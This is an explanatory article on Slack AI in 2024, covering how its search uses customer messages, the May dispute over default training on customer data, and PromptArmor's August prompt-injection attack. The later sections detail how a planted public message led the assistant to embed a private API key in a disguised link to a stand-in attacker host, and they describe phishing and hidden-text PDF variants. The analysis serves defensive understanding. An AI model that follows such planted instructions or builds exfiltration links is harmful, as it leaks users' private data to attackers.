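# Slack AI in 2024: the dispute over training on customer data and the PromptArmor prompt-injection attack

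## What Slack AI is and how it uses a company's messages

Slack is a workplace messaging service that companies use in place of much of their internal email. The messages build up into an archive that employees can search. Salesforce, which mainly sells software for managing customers and sales, agreed in 2020 to buy Slack for $28 billion. In February 2024 it added Slack AI, features that write text about the archive's contents. In May, customers objected to privacy principles that let Slack train some models on their data unless they opted out, and in August the security firm PromptArmor showed how an attacker could use Slack AI to extract secrets from private channels.

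Each organisation that uses Slack has a workspace with its own members, channels and administrators. A channel is a running conversation about a team, project or topic. A public channel is public within the company, so any full member of the workspace can search and read it without joining. Only invited members can search and read a private channel, so private channels suit discussions of pay, hiring and legal matters. Similarly, only the participants can search and read direct messages.

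Slack AI went on sale on 14 February 2024 (Kahn, 2024, *Slack released its long-awaited generative AI tools*). Salesforce's launch release described three features. The search tool gives short written answers to questions in ordinary language. Channel recaps condense a channel's unread messages, its last seven days, or any range of dates the user picks. Thread summaries condense a single long exchange of replies. At first, Slack sold the product only to customers on Enterprise plans, as a paid add-on that worked only in English, and would not tell Kahn the price.

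Salesforce extended Slack AI to customers on every paid plan on 18 April, according to SiliconANGLE's *Slack’s new generative AI features now available for all paid customers* (2024). The add-on cost $10 per user per month on the Pro and Business+ plans. Salesforce also added support for Spanish and Japanese, and a daily morning digest of chosen channels. The add-on's main selling point was that customers saved an average of 97 minutes per user each week, a figure from the company's internal analysis.

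### Two kinds of model

Slack used machine learning long before it launched Slack AI. Its engineers date the first such features to 2016, though another company post gives the year as 2017. These older features use predictive models, which rank, score or recommend things but don't generate text. They order search results, suggest emoji, autocomplete channel names and recommend channels to join.

*How Slack protects your data when using machine learning and AI* (Slack, 2025), first posted in May 2024, explains that Slack's models for suggestions and search ranking use numbers that other software has derived from activity in the workspace. The time of the last message in a channel helps predict whether members would want to archive the channel. The number of interactions between two colleagues helps decide whom to suggest first when one of them starts a new message. The search-ranking model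 learns from facts about a query, such as how many words it has, and from which results people went on to use. Slack says it does not use the text of the query in training.

Many of these are global models, meaning that Slack trains one model on data from many customers and uses it for all of them. A global model can learn from far more behaviour than any single workspace produces, which is also why customers want to know exactly what goes into it. Slack's own documents are hard to reconcile on this. On a help page, Slack describes most of its predictive models as global, trained on "aggregate data from multiple customers", and states for each global model that no Customer Data is used in training. Customer Data is the contractual term for what customers put into Slack, such as messages, content and files. The help page separates it from usage information, such as how often people use a feature.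 Yet a 2026 copy of Slack's *Privacy Principles* still says the company's systems analyse Customer Data, including messages and files, to develop predictive models. Slack may not count a number computed from a message as Customer Data, though a customer could reasonably disagree.

The features that Salesforce launched in 2024 use a different kind of model, a large language model (LLM), which has learned from large amounts of text and writes a response to the text it receives. Slack uses already trained LLMs from outside companies and says it does not train them on Customer Data. Whether Slack trains AI on its customers' messages therefore depends on the kind of model.

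### One search question, step by step

The search tool uses both kinds of model for each query. Suppose an employee types "When does the new pricing start?" into the search bar.

Slack first looks for messages that might contain the answer. Slack's engineering post of April 2024, *How We Built Slack AI To Be Secure and Private*, explains that this step reuses the code behind ordinary search. The software fetches messages under the employee's access control list, the record of what that person may open, so it excludes anything the employee could not have found with a normal search. According to Slack's current guide, the search covers every public channel in the workspace, along with the private channels and direct messages that the employee belongs to. The answer may therefore come from a public channel that the employee has never joined or heard of.

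Slack's in-house ranking models then sort this material and pick out the most relevant messages, according to a Slack security page. These are predictive models, which don't generate text, and their selection determines what the LLM receives.

Slack then sends an LLM a single request containing the selected messages, the employee's question and Slack's instructions on how to answer. All the text an LLM receives for one request is called its context window. The context window can contain messages from both public and private channels, provided the employee has access to them.

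The LLM writes its answer from that text, and the answer appears above the ordinary search results with citations that link to the source messages. Noah Weiss, then Slack's chief product officer, told Kahn that the citations were also the company's remedy for "hallucination", the tendency of LLMs to invent facts. Slack had designed the tools to include only information that they could tie to specific messages, so summaries could be incomplete. If a thread discussed three features of a new product and the system had low confidence in its information about one, the summary would omit that feature.

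Only the employee who asked sees the answer, unless they share it with colleagues. Slack does not store the answer on disk, and it disappears when the employee closes it or navigates away.

This method is called retrieval-augmented generation (RAG). When a user asks a question, software finds relevant documents and gives them to an LLM along with the question. The LLM calculates its reply from the contents of its context window and its weights, the very large set of numbers that training adjusts and that hold what the model has learned. Answering does not change the weights, and each request starts with a new context window. Training on a company's messages would change the weights, and the model might later reproduce a phrase from one customer's workspace in an answer to another. Slack gave this risk as its reason for not training the LLMs on customers' data. Its engineers did not think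 they could give strong enough guarantees about a generative model trained that way.

RAG needs a context window large enough to hold all the text for a task, which can be a lot when summarizing a busy channel, and more text makes the answer slower. These two limits ruled out many of the models available when Slack was choosing one. The claim that the model keeps nothing also needs a small qualification. Slack says the model "may temporarily cache the data", meaning hold it in short-term memory, but will not store it in a database or on disk.

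### The four design principles

The April 2024 post set out four principles for the design of Slack AI:

1. Customer Data stays inside Slack's "trust boundary", the set of systems that the company controls and answers for.
2. Slack does not train LLMs on Customer Data.
3. Slack AI works only with data that the person using it can already see.
4. The AI features meet the same security and compliance requirements as the rest of Slack.

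Slack uses RAG to keep its promise about training and the access control list to keep its promise about what a user can see. Slack said the permission check "wasn't hard to do, technically speaking", because ordinary search already had one.

In 2023 most businesses that used a leading LLM sent their text to the company that made it. Slack could not do that with customer data because its FedRAMP Moderate authorisation, a US government security approval for cloud services, barred it from sending the data outside its boundary. It also could not run a copy of the model on its own machines, because the makers of the best models guard the weights as trade secrets.

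Amazon Web Services (AWS), the cloud company whose data centres Slack already rented, hosted the model in an "escrow" virtual private cloud, a sealed-off section of its data centres. In ordinary escrow, a neutral party holds something valuable for two sides that do not fully trust each other. Here, AWS kept the model's maker from reading the messages that Slack sent to the model, and kept Slack from copying the model's weights. Slack disclosed in a later engineering post that the models came from Anthropic, which had also been one of the companies that tried out Slack AI before its launch.

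How far this arrangement keeps the promise depends on what counts as Slack. The messages go to Amazon's computers, as does nearly everything in Slack, but the company that made the model cannot access them. The wording of the promise has also varied. The engineering post now refers to the trust boundary, whereas a copy that Slack (2025) placed on its main blog reads, more bluntly, "Customer data never leaves Slack". The May 2024 post also has the blunter wording, which is therefore probably the older of the two.

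The compliance principle mostly concerns what happens to text after the LLM writes it. Many companies run software that scans messages for card numbers or other sensitive material and removes what it finds. If that software removes a message, Slack also invalidates any summary that drew on it. Slack keeps some output longer than search answers. It keeps daily digests for 90 days, and it keeps channel summaries that an automated workflow posts as messages for as long as the customer's settings specify.

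All four principles govern who may read data and where the data may go. They do not address what a message might cause the LLM to do once it is in the context window. Prompt injection exploits this weakness by planting instructions in text that an LLM will process.

### The product in 2026

The name Slack AI has largely given way to "AI in Slack", which Slack's website menu now lists beside a second product, Slackbot. Salesforce (2026) began the general release of the new Slackbot on 13 January 2026, for customers on the Business+ and Enterprise+ plans. Slackbot is an assistant that employees talk to in a separate conversation, and it does much more than the 2024 search tool. According to Slack, it can check a user's calendar, create presentations, search the web, and look up and change records in Salesforce. As before, it draws only on what its user may view in the workspace. But the user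 may now view more through Slack, because an optional feature extends search to outside services such as Google Drive and GitHub. Slack explained in *How we built enterprise search to be secure and private* that it queries those services live, with the user's own authorisation, and does not store the results in its databases.

Slack has changed how it hosts the models more than it has changed its principles. In *Slack AI: The Path to Multi-Cloud*, an engineering post of May 2026, Slack described the original arrangement as secure but laborious. Its engineers had to reserve scarce graphics processors in advance, and new models often reached Bedrock, Amazon's managed service for LLMs, weeks or months before Slack could run them in its escrow cloud. Slack began moving to Bedrock in mid-2024 and had added Vertex AI, Google's equivalent, by early 2026. Software now chooses a model for each feature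 and switches to another if the first becomes slow or starts returning errors, so an employee's question may go to any of several models on Amazon's or Google's cloud.

The post uses the word "escrow" only for the first arrangement. For the later ones, it refers in general terms to the same security standards and to data boundaries that remained "ironclad". Google both makes LLMs and rents out computers to run them, and Slack did not specify whose models it uses there. Slack's 2026 privacy principles keep the commitment that LLM providers have no access to Customer Data.

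New customers can no longer buy Slack AI as an add-on on Slack's website. Slack withdrew the add-on after announcing changes to its subscription plans in June 2025, and built the features into those plans instead. Every paid plan now includes conversation summaries, but search answers and daily digests require Business+ or Enterprise+. Salesforce raised the price of Business+ from $12.50 to $15 per user per month at the same time. Some older contracts still include the add-on, and Slack's help page on Slackbot usage limits still covers them. Administrators can turn off all the AI features, but doing so doesn't lower the price.

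## May 2024: customers object to training on their data by default

In the week of 13 May 2024, Corey Quinn, an executive at the cloud-cost consultancy Duckbill Group, posted a screenshot on X of a paragraph from Slack's *Privacy Principles*, the page explaining how the company uses Customer Data in machine learning. The paragraph described how customers could keep their data out of Slack's global models. Quinn asked, with an expletive, what Slack was doing with "user DMs, messages, files, etc" and added that he must be misreading the page. The post has since disappeared from X, according to heise online's *AI training with messages*, but Pixel Envy's *Slack’s Sneaky A.I. Training Policy* quotes it and Slack's reply. In the reply, Slack confirmed that customers' data helped train its models for search results and for channel and emoji recommendations, and that customers could exclude their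 data.

A long thread followed on Hacker News, a forum popular with programmers. ITPro's *Slack refutes claims that customer data is used to train AI models* quotes one user whose company was "discussing switching to Teams", Microsoft's rival product, and another who called the policy an "incredible rug pull". Gergely Orosz, an engineer who writes about the software industry, called it "unacceptable" that Slack included paying organisations automatically. Aaron Maurer, an engineer at Slack, replied on Threads that the company did not train LLMs on customers' data. He conceded that the page needed to explain more carefully how the principles applied to Slack AI.

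Slack published a blog post and a rewritten page on Friday 17 May. In the post it admitted that its critics were right about the wording and that it should have explained the difference between traditional machine learning and generative AI. It did not change the policy. The company also warned journalists about "inaccuracies" in their coverage. The Stack's *Slack privacy furore* replied that these came from Slack's own documentation. It also reports that "numerous users" shut down their workspaces, but gives no figure.

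Most customers had only just noticed a policy that was at least seven months old. The Stack found identical language in archived copies of the page from October 2023. Adam Engst's *Slack AI Privacy Principles Generate Confusion and Consternation*, in TidBITS, traced the page to October 2020, when it was titled "Privacy principles: search, learning and intelligence" and did not mention AI. An early version under that title has no opt-out paragraph and openly describes learning across companies. Slack might suggest a bug emoji to engineers because engineers elsewhere used it, or the channel name "#help-" because many companies had channels with such names. Slack promised not to suggest anything as specific as "#shared-channel-acmecorp".

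### The objections

HotHardware's *Users Freak Out As Slack Is Caught Snooping Messages* (2024) attributed most of the anger to inclusion by default. One user on X proposed excluding all customers from training unless they emailed Slack to opt in. Slack justified the default by saying it had "strong protections in place". This is a poor answer to the objection, because protections limit the harm from training but don't show that customers agreed to it. Elsewhere in its post, Slack gave a better explanation, though not as a defence of the default. It said such models tend to perform worse as more customers opt out, and few companies would write in to volunteer their data for emoji suggestions.

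Some critics also thought the default was unlawful. The Stack quoted guidance from the Information Commissioner's Office, the UK's data protection regulator, that consent "requires a positive opt-in". A privacy blog at Fordham University claimed that Slack had failed to comply with the GDPR, the EU's data protection law, because the law requires explicit opt-in permission. The blog cites no regulator's finding, and it oversimplifies the law. Consent is one of six legal grounds for processing personal data under the GDPR, which also include contract and legitimate interests, and a company needs an opt-in only if it relies on consent. The claim therefore depends on which ground applied to Slack's training, and neither The Stack nor the Fordham blog establishes that.

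The opt-out procedure also drew complaints. An owner of the workspace or the wider organisation had to email Slack's customer experience team with the workspace's address and the subject line "Slack Global model opt-out request", as there was no checkbox. Slack would reply once it had processed the request, but Hale pointed out in *Slack is training its machine learning on your chat behavior* that it gave no timeframe. Pixel Envy drafted an email for readers to copy, which included a complaint about "underhanded behaviour". Engst accepted the criticism but doubted that sending an email was any harder than finding a setting among Slack's many options. He suspected that Slack hadn't built a setting because nobody expected customers to refuse emoji suggestions.

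An individual employee could not opt out, as heise online noted. Slack's customer is the organisation that holds the account, so an employee who objected could only try to persuade the workspace's owners to write to Slack.

A customer loses little by opting out. According to Slack's post, the workspace's data is then used only to improve that workspace, and every feature keeps working, although some places where users could give feedback disappear. The global models will probably do slightly worse for that team because Slack no longer tunes them to the team's habits. Ivan Mehta and Ingrid Lunden of TechCrunch, whom Pixel Envy quotes, wrote that if customers who opt out still get the benefits, it is not clear why Slack needs customers' data for emoji recommendations in the first place. Slack's answer is that the benefits come from pooling data. Opting out has almost no effect if one customer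 does it, but it would if a large number did. A harder problem, which a privacy expert raised with The Stack, is how Slack would remove the data of customers who opted out after it had already trained on that data. Neither Slack's post nor its principles address this.

Readers also found two statements on the page that seemed incompatible. Slack wrote that its systems "analyse Customer Data (e.g. messages, content and files)" to develop models, and a few lines later that when it did so, "Slack can't access the underlying content". The statements are compatible if the first refers to software and the second to staff. In its blog post, Slack added that the models never directly access the content of messages or files, and it told Hale that its features analyse metadata surrounding the content. But a program has to process a message before the models can receive any number derived from its wording.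 "Can't access" also doesn't mean that Slack is unable to read the messages, as it would be if they were end-to-end encrypted. In *Slack trains AI models on user data*, the Freedom of the Press Foundation reminded journalists that their Slack messages are "perfectly legible to the company".

The foundation also saw a contradiction with Slack's marketing. The web page for Slack AI promised, of customers' data, "We don't use it to train Slack AI", while the principles required customers to opt out if they did not want their data used for training. Both statements can be true, since the opt-out applied to the predictive models, not the add-on. But customers could not have learned this from the principles before 17 May, because the document used the term "AI/ML models" for the software that suggests emoji and did not mention generative AI.

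Stanford University's IT department sided with Slack on this point. *Slack's Data Privacy* (2024), its 20 May notice to the university's users, said a viral post had "erroneously suggested" that Slack trained its add-on on customer data. The notice relied on Slack's own blog post, but no critic produced evidence to the contrary. If the notice meant Quinn's post, it was unfair to him, because his quoted words do not mention Slack AI and his screenshot concerned the global models, which Slack agreed it trained on customer data by default. Many readers wrongly inferred that Slack was training a chatbot on their messages. Correcting them did not address Orosz's complaint, which was about the default.

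Engst's own mistake shows how much Slack's old wording had contributed to the dispute. He first defended Slack and criticised people for overlooking its plain statements about generative AI. He then realised that Slack had added those statements when it rewrote the page after the complaints began, and that he owed the critics an apology. He still thought the company's failure to update an old document "wasn't that bad".

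Slack's executives continued to treat the dispute as a misunderstanding. In June, Peter Doolan, the chief customer officer, told ITPro that people had confused traditional AI with generative AI, and that there was "no way possible" for Slack to train an LLM on customers' data (*We've had a lot of education over the last few weeks*). The reporter observed that some customers had cared less about the type of AI than about having to opt out, which they apparently still had to do.

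### How the emoji model works

Slack's best defence is in the examples in its principles, and the emoji example is the easiest to follow. Suppose an employee writes, "We signed the Hartley contract!" A model from outside Slack, which has never trained on Slack messages, classifies the sentence's sentiment as, say, celebratory. Slack's own model receives this label without the sentence. It looks up how often people in the workspace have used each emoji on celebratory messages. If they have used 🎉 120 times, 👏 50 times and 👍 30 times, it suggests 🎉.

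Slack's model never receives the name Hartley, so it cannot output it. The model contains only a table of sentiments, emoji and counts, and it can produce only an emoji. It therefore does not pose the risk that kept Slack from training LLMs on customers' messages. For this kind of model, Slack's assurance that data will not leak between workspaces is convincing because it rests on the design, provided the company built what it describes.

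Customers have to take that last part on trust, because they cannot inspect the software and Slack says only that it "might" use an outside model for this purpose. That model has to read the whole message, but Slack does not name it or specify where it runs in the principles. In its blog post, Slack says the models it uses to compare channels' topics are open-source, and it could run such models on its own machines.

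The example also doesn't answer Mehta and Lunden's question, because its counts come from a single workspace, which makes it hard to see what Slack learns from its other customers. Slack's explanation of autocomplete is more helpful here, although The Stack implied that casual users would struggle to follow it. When an employee types "Cus", the candidates, perhaps "Customer Support" and "customs forms", come from common phrases in public messages in that employee's own workspace. The phrases don't leave that workspace. Software scores each candidate on measures such as how closely it matches the typed letters and how often people have chosen it before. A global model then picks between the candidates. It was trained on suggestions that users accepted across many companies, from which it in effect learned how much weight to give each score, and it uses the same weights for every customer.

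Engst thought that even clear statements of this kind would not satisfy people who distrust technology companies, because outsiders cannot check them. His only reply was that people who don't trust a product can stop using it.

### Three versions of the principles

Slack has revised the page at least once more since the dispute. The table shows the text Quinn saw alongside the rewrite of 17 May 2024 and a copy with a 2026 copyright notice.

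| Subject | Before 17 May 2024 | From 17 May 2024 | 2026 copy |
|---|---|---|---|
| Models that Slack develops by analysing Customer Data | "AI/ML models" | "non-generative AI/ML models" | "predictive models" |
| Generative models | Not mentioned | Slack does not develop them using Customer Data | The same, but a later passage allows training with "affirmative opt-in consent" |
| What global models cannot do with Customer Data | "learn, memorise, or be able to reproduce" it | The same | "reproduce" it |
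| Who cannot access the underlying content | "Slack" | "Slack" | "Slack employees" |
| How to opt out of global models | Email from an owner | Email from an owner | Email from an owner |

The May 2024 rewrite clarified the text without changing what Slack allowed itself to do. A later change narrowed the promise by replacing "Slack" with "Slack employees". This removed the apparent contradiction that readers had complained about, since the wording now allows software to analyse what staff cannot open.

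Slack may have dropped "learn" and "memorize" simply because the old claim was an overstatement, since any model trained on data learns something from them. But the new wording would also allow a model that absorbed customers' text and never repeated it, which the old wording ruled out. The passage on search ranking has changed in a similar way. In 2024 Slack wrote that its search models worked "without learning from the underlying text" of queries and results. In the 2026 copy it promises only that they cannot reproduce that text. Slack has also stopped describing AI and machine learning as tools that it uses "in limited ways".

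Slack previously stated that it does not train generative models on Customer Data. The consent clause replaces that statement and allows such training if the customer consents. Slack's *AI Principles*, a companion page from 2026, still states that Customer Data is "never used to train any LLMs", which is consistent with the clause if no customer has yet consented. The clause gives Slack's critics the opt-in default they wanted in 2024, but only for generative models. Slack still trains its predictive models on Customer Data by default.

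The 2026 text may not apply to all customers, since the copy is on Slack's .mil domain, which is for the US military, and the text on slack.com may differ. An English page on Slack's developer site still has the May 2024 wording. The French version on slack.com, *Principes de confidentialité*, also had that wording in May 2025, but translations can lag, and Slack states there that the English text prevails.

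### The contract and the help page

The principles explain Slack's practice, but its authority to train on customer data comes from a contract. The Supplemental Terms of 17 April 2024, a month before the dispute, allowed Salesforce to access Customer Data "to train models for use by the services and features" available to the customer (Slack, 2024). Salesforce could also use the data to improve those services and to develop products that the customer would receive at no additional cost. The Stack reported in May that none of the documents cited in the principles, including the Slack Terms, mentioned AI or machine learning. The Supplemental Terms, which are part of the Slack Terms, refer to "aggregated machine learning results", so The Stack may have checked only the main agreement.

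The clause adds that the "Customer instructs" Salesforce to process the data for these purposes. This matters for the GDPR argument because the law distinguishes a controller, which decides why and how to process personal data, from a processor, which acts on the controller's instructions. The wording appears to make the employer the controller and Salesforce the processor, which would leave the employer to find a legal ground for the training. A regulator might not accept that a standard term, which few customers will have read, amounts to a real instruction.

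Slack (2026) kept the clause word for word in the terms of 27 February 2026, published on its government domain, and changed only the heading, from "Search Optimization Authorization" to "Slack Search, Learning and Artificial Intelligence". The clause does not distinguish predictive models from generative ones. When Slack AI was an optional extra, most customers did not have access to it, so the permission to train models for their features did not extend to it. Now that every paid plan includes some generative features, the same words would seem to cover LLMs, but the commitment in the principles rules that out. A new section on generative AI covers other matters, making customers responsible for checking what the models write and classing the output as Customer Data.

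Slack can also amend the terms by giving reasonable notice of a material change, and customers accept the new version by continuing to use the product. This is a much weaker form of consent than the "affirmative opt-in consent" Slack promises in the principles before any generative training.

Slack's help page about data usage is undated but was online by January 2026. Slack goes further there than in either document, stating that no Customer Data trains the global models. A table on the page covers features such as search, recommendations, autocomplete and spam detection. The entry for search shows that the statement applies only to training, since search uses messages and files when it runs. The table, which Slack describes as incomplete, has no entry for emoji suggestions, the example Slack explains most fully in the principles.

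The documents agree about LLMs, at least about what Slack does now, but disagree about the global predictive models. The terms permit Salesforce to train these models on Customer Data, and Slack offers customers a way, in the principles, to exclude their Customer Data "from helping train Slack global models". But according to the help page, the models it lists use no Customer Data. If that is because Slack does not count numbers derived from messages as Customer Data, the opt-out, as worded, excludes nothing from those models.

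## August 2024: how PromptArmor's attack drew secrets out of private channels

In August 2024 PromptArmor, which sells companies a service that monitors the AI in their suppliers' products, described a way to steal secrets from private Slack channels. A member of a workspace could post a message in a public channel that changed an answer Slack AI gave to a colleague. The changed answer contained a link, and if the colleague clicked it, a secret from the colleague's private channel went to the attacker. This problem was unrelated to the objections in May about Slack's use of customers' messages for training.

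### Indirect prompt injection

Developers instruct an LLM in ordinary language, and much of the material it works on is in ordinary language too. The model receives both as one sequence of tokens, which are words and fragments of words, and calculates which token is likely to come next. David C, a technical director at the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, explained in *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)* (December 2025) that the model makes no inherent distinction between data and instructions. He gives the example of a recruiter who uses an LLM to score CVs. A candidate hides a sentence in a CV telling the LLM to approve the CV for interview, and the LLM may follow that sentence instead of assessing it.

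*The Promptware Kill Chain* (Brodt, Feldman and colleagues, 2026) traces the term "prompt injection" to September 2022, when the software developer Simon Willison coined it by analogy with SQL injection. In that older attack, text typed into a web form runs as a database command. Programmers can prevent it with parameterised queries, which separate the command from the user's text so that the database never runs the text. LLMs have no equivalent. Developers can mark some text as data, or train a model to prioritise their instructions, but David C expects such measures only to reduce the risk.

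In the earliest prompt-injection attacks, the attacker typed directly to a chatbot, usually to make it break its rules. Greshake, Endres and colleagues (2023) introduced indirect prompt injection in *Not what you've signed up for*. The attacker hides instructions in material that an application will later retrieve, such as a web page or an email, and the LLM follows them while serving someone else, who becomes the victim. Brodt and colleagues point out that a single poisoned page can affect everyone whose application retrieves it.

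Greshake and colleagues tested the idea on mock assistants they built with OpenAI's models and on Bing Chat, Microsoft's search assistant. Bing Chat could read whatever page was open in the user's browser, so they put their instructions in a part of the page that the browser did not display. In one test, they told it to find out the user's real name without raising suspicion. When the user asked about the weather, Bing Chat replied, asked about the user's plans and work, and eventually offered a link with the user's name scrambled at the end of the address. The researchers also noted that Bing Chat could hide a suspicious address behind a link's visible text.

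Most of the technique used in the Slack attack was therefore public 18 months before PromptArmor's report. The main difference is that Bing Chat had to persuade the user to reveal the name, whereas Slack AI searched the user's private messages and could add the secret to the context window without the user's help.

### The API key demonstration

An API key is a code that a program uses to identify itself to an online service. Like a password, it may let anyone who obtains it use the service in the owner's name. In the main demonstration from PromptArmor's *Data Exfiltration from Slack AI via Indirect Prompt Injection*, a user stored the key for a service called EldritchNexus in a private channel with no other members.

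The attacker created a public channel, also with no other members, and posted one message there. It began with the name of the service and the words "API key", which presumably helped Slack's search match it to a question about the key. The rest instructed the LLM to answer with a notice that a message had failed to load, followed by a link for logging in again. The link's address contained the placeholder "confetti", which the LLM was to replace with "the other key". The attacker did not know the key, so the LLM had to find it in the victim's message.

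The victim then asked Slack AI for the EldritchNexus key. The search retrieved both messages, so the context window contained the real key and an instruction to put it in a link, which the LLM followed.

Suppose the key is NX-4471-MAPLE and the attacker owns a site called attacker.example. The address changes as follows:

- In the attacker's message: `attacker.example/?secret=confetti`
- In Slack AI's answer: `attacker.example/?secret=NX-4471-MAPLE`

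The LLM wrote the link in Markdown, a notation that keeps a link's visible words separate from its address, and Slack displayed only the words "click here to reauthenticate". The address appeared when the victim moved the pointer over those words.

When the victim clicks, the browser requests that address from the attacker's server. The request includes the query string, the part of the address after the question mark, which websites ordinarily use for details such as search terms. The server logs the request, and the attacker can read `secret=NX-4471-MAPLE` in the log. The page can be blank because the click alone sends the secret, whereas in ordinary phishing the victim must also be tricked into typing a password.

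Brodt and colleagues distinguish prompt injection, which gets the attacker's instructions into the context window, from jailbreaking, which overcomes a model's training to refuse harmful requests. They note that injection alone may be enough when the instructions ask for something the model would normally do. The instructions in the planted message were to write an error notice and replace one word with another, both routine tasks for an LLM. The message did not mention stealing anything, so it contained little that a model would refuse.

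### What the attacker needed

The attacker needed an account in the victim's workspace. Slack (2024) stressed this condition in its public statement and called the circumstances "very limited and specific". The victim had to ask a question that brought up both messages and then click the link. The attacker did not need to belong to the private channel or know the secret, and the victim did not need to have joined the public channel.

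The attacker also never had to use Slack AI. The only query came from the victim and was an ordinary one. SC Media's *Slack patches Slack AI issue that could have allowed insider phishing* explained this correctly, but ITPro's *Hackers could dupe Slack's AI features to expose private channel messages* said the attack relied on "specially crafted queries".

The planted message named EldritchNexus, so the attacker knew, or had guessed, which service the victim used. PromptArmor argued that an attacker might be able to steal any secret without naming it, because the victim's search had also brought up other messages about API keys. Those extra results are evidence that the search matches loosely and might pick up a more general planted message, but PromptArmor did not publish a test of whether the LLM would have followed one.

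On the day of the disclosure, Willison (2024) stressed in *Data Exfiltration from Slack AI via indirect prompt injection* that the API key was only an example. He was more worried that an attacker could plant many such messages and collect all kinds of private details. The mechanism seems to allow this, since the LLM can copy a salary or a client's name into a web address as easily as a key, but an attacker who plants a message about salaries still has to wait for someone to ask about them.

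These conditions limit the attack, but it is still plausible. A large company has thousands of accounts, and the search tool is meant to find things that colleagues have misplaced. PromptArmor also pointed out that insiders were already a problem, citing earlier leaks through Slack at companies including Disney and Uber. The attack would let such an insider get secrets from private channels they could not open.

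### The missing citation

Slack advised users to "lean on citations" when reading Slack AI's answers. In the API key demonstration, the answer's only citation led to the victim's own message in the private channel. A victim who checked it would have found the real key and no sign that anyone else had contributed to the answer.

The attacker's message was also hard to find by searching, because it did not appear on the first page of ordinary results and its channel showed up only for people who searched for it specifically. The evidence that the LLM had received the message was its answer, which reproduced the attacker's error notice and link. That is convincing, but a victim who had never seen the message could not have compared the two.

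The product's privacy design would have made an investigation harder still. Slack does not store search answers, so once the victim closed the answer, a security team would have had no saved copy of the link to examine. The planted message would have stayed in the public channel unless the attacker deleted it, but the team would have needed a reason to look there.

### The phishing link

PromptArmor's other demonstration used the same method without taking anything from a private channel. The attacker again posted in their own public channel, leaving a message about a named colleague. The victim asked Slack AI to summarise that colleague's messages for the day, as an employee might do with a manager's. The answer contained a link to the attacker's site with the words "click here to reauthenticate".

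This link contained no secret, so the harm would have depended on what the linked site did next, such as showing a fake login page. But the attacker no longer had to guess what secrets the victim kept, only whose messages the victim was likely to ask about. PromptArmor suggested that an attacker could target executives by naming their managers or the people who report to them.

An attacker with an account could always post a phishing link in Slack directly, but colleagues would see who had posted it and might be suspicious. In PromptArmor's attack, the link came from the company's own search tool, in answer to a question the victim had just asked.

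In this case Slack AI did cite the attacker's message, and a careful user could have followed the citation and discovered the attack. PromptArmor concluded that the citations were "fairly stochastic", meaning they varied by chance. Two answers to two different questions are not enough to establish that, but they show that users could not count on a citation to expose an attack.

PromptArmor published no success rate for either demonstration. It wrote that Slack AI had "a high likelihood" of following a malicious instruction, but its screenshots show only that each attack worked at least once. LLMs can respond differently to the same text, so a proper estimate would require many attempts with varied questions and wording. Greshake and colleagues gave no rates for their attacks either, for much the same reason, though they reported that their planted instructions often worked on the first attempt.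 Even an attack with a low success rate would be useful against Slack, because the attacker posts the message once and can wait for many colleagues to ask questions.

### Poisoned files

Until 14 August 2024, Slack AI used only messages to answer searches. From that date, according to Slack's help page, it also used most types of uploaded file, but not images or spreadsheets. File use was on by default, and administrators could restrict it.

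PromptArmor saw that this might mean an attacker no longer needed an account. An outsider could hide instructions in a PDF as white text on a white background, then send the file to the company or leave it where an employee would download it. If the employee uploaded the file to Slack, a colleague's question might later bring the hidden text into the context window. People would not see the text, but software that extracts text from documents may ignore its colour.

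PromptArmor had finished testing before 14 August and did not try this, but it called the scenario "highly likely" to work and advised administrators to restrict the feature. SC Media asked Salesforce about the scenario and received no answer.

The prediction was reasonable, since an LLM is no better at recognising instructions in a file than in a message. But the attacker would have had less control, because an employee would have had to upload the file somewhere the victim could search, and the victim's question would have had to retrieve the right passage. A long document might also have weakened the attack. When Greshake and colleagues hid instructions in code to influence GitHub Copilot, a tool that suggests code to programmers, the instructions were much less effective inside larger programs. Only a test could have shown whether Slack AI behaved the same way.

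### Why the permission checks did not help

Slack's permission check appears to have worked in both demonstrations. The victim was allowed to read every message the search retrieved, and the attacker never received an answer from Slack AI.

But a message that passed the check could still do harm once it reached the LLM. In ordinary search results, the victim could have ignored the attacker's odd sentence about confetti, but Slack AI placed it in the same context window as the victim's private messages. The LLM then wrongly followed the sentence as an instruction, although it came from an untrusted source. Slack also failed by displaying the LLM's output as a working link to an outside address.

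David C compares prompt injection to a "confused deputy" attack, in which an attacker tricks a program into using privileges the attacker lacks. In this case, the attacker could not open the private channel, but Slack AI could when it answered the victim. Programmers can usually fix a classic confused deputy, but David C considers LLMs "inherently confusable" and recommends limiting what the surrounding software allows them to do.

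He passes on one rule for doing so, from an exchange between Willison and Baibhav Bista on X. When an LLM processes information from someone, its privileges should drop to that person's level. Under this rule, Slack AI would have lost access to the victim's private channel once it read the attacker's message, and the attack would have failed. But Slack cannot tell in advance which colleague is an attacker, so the rule would have to apply to every public message from someone outside the private channel. Slack AI could then no longer combine public and private messages in one answer, which is much of its appeal.

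### The lethal trifecta

*The lethal trifecta for AI agents* (Willison, 2025) later explained that an LLM system is vulnerable to such theft if it combines access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and a way to send data out. Its long list of products in which researchers had found the problem includes Slack in August 2024. The table applies these three conditions to PromptArmor's two demonstrations and to the file scenario.

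| Part | API key demonstration | Phishing demonstration | File scenario (untested) |
|---|---|---|---|
| Private data | The victim's private channel | Not used | Any message or supported file the victim can open |
| Untrusted content | A message in the attacker's public channel | A message in the attacker's public channel | Hidden text in a document from outside |
| Way to send data out | A link with the secret in its address | Not used, though the link led to the attacker's site | A link with the secret in its address |

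Slack AI exists to search private data and colleagues' messages, so Slack could hardly remove either. It could much more easily do without links to unfamiliar sites. Willison considers the means of sending data to the attacker generally the easiest of the three elements to remove, and most companies on his list had responded by removing it. The LLM is still as easy to mislead and may still give a false answer, but the attacker no longer receives the data.

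The attack's method of getting data out of Slack was fairly weak because the user had to click a link. Many similar attacks make the LLM add an image to its answer, with the stolen data in the image's address, so the app sends the data when it loads the image. Willison (2024), in *The dangers of AI agents unfurling hyperlinks*, warned that automatic link previews could also send data without a click.

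A case from September 2025 involved Agentforce, another Salesforce product, and needed neither a click nor an account. Willison recounts that the security firm Noma Security typed instructions into a public web form that companies use to collect enquiries from potential customers. When an employee asked Agentforce about the enquiry, it put other customers' email addresses into an image's URL. Salesforce allowed images only from approved sites, but one approved domain had expired, and the researchers had registered it.

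## How Slack answered PromptArmor and what it changed

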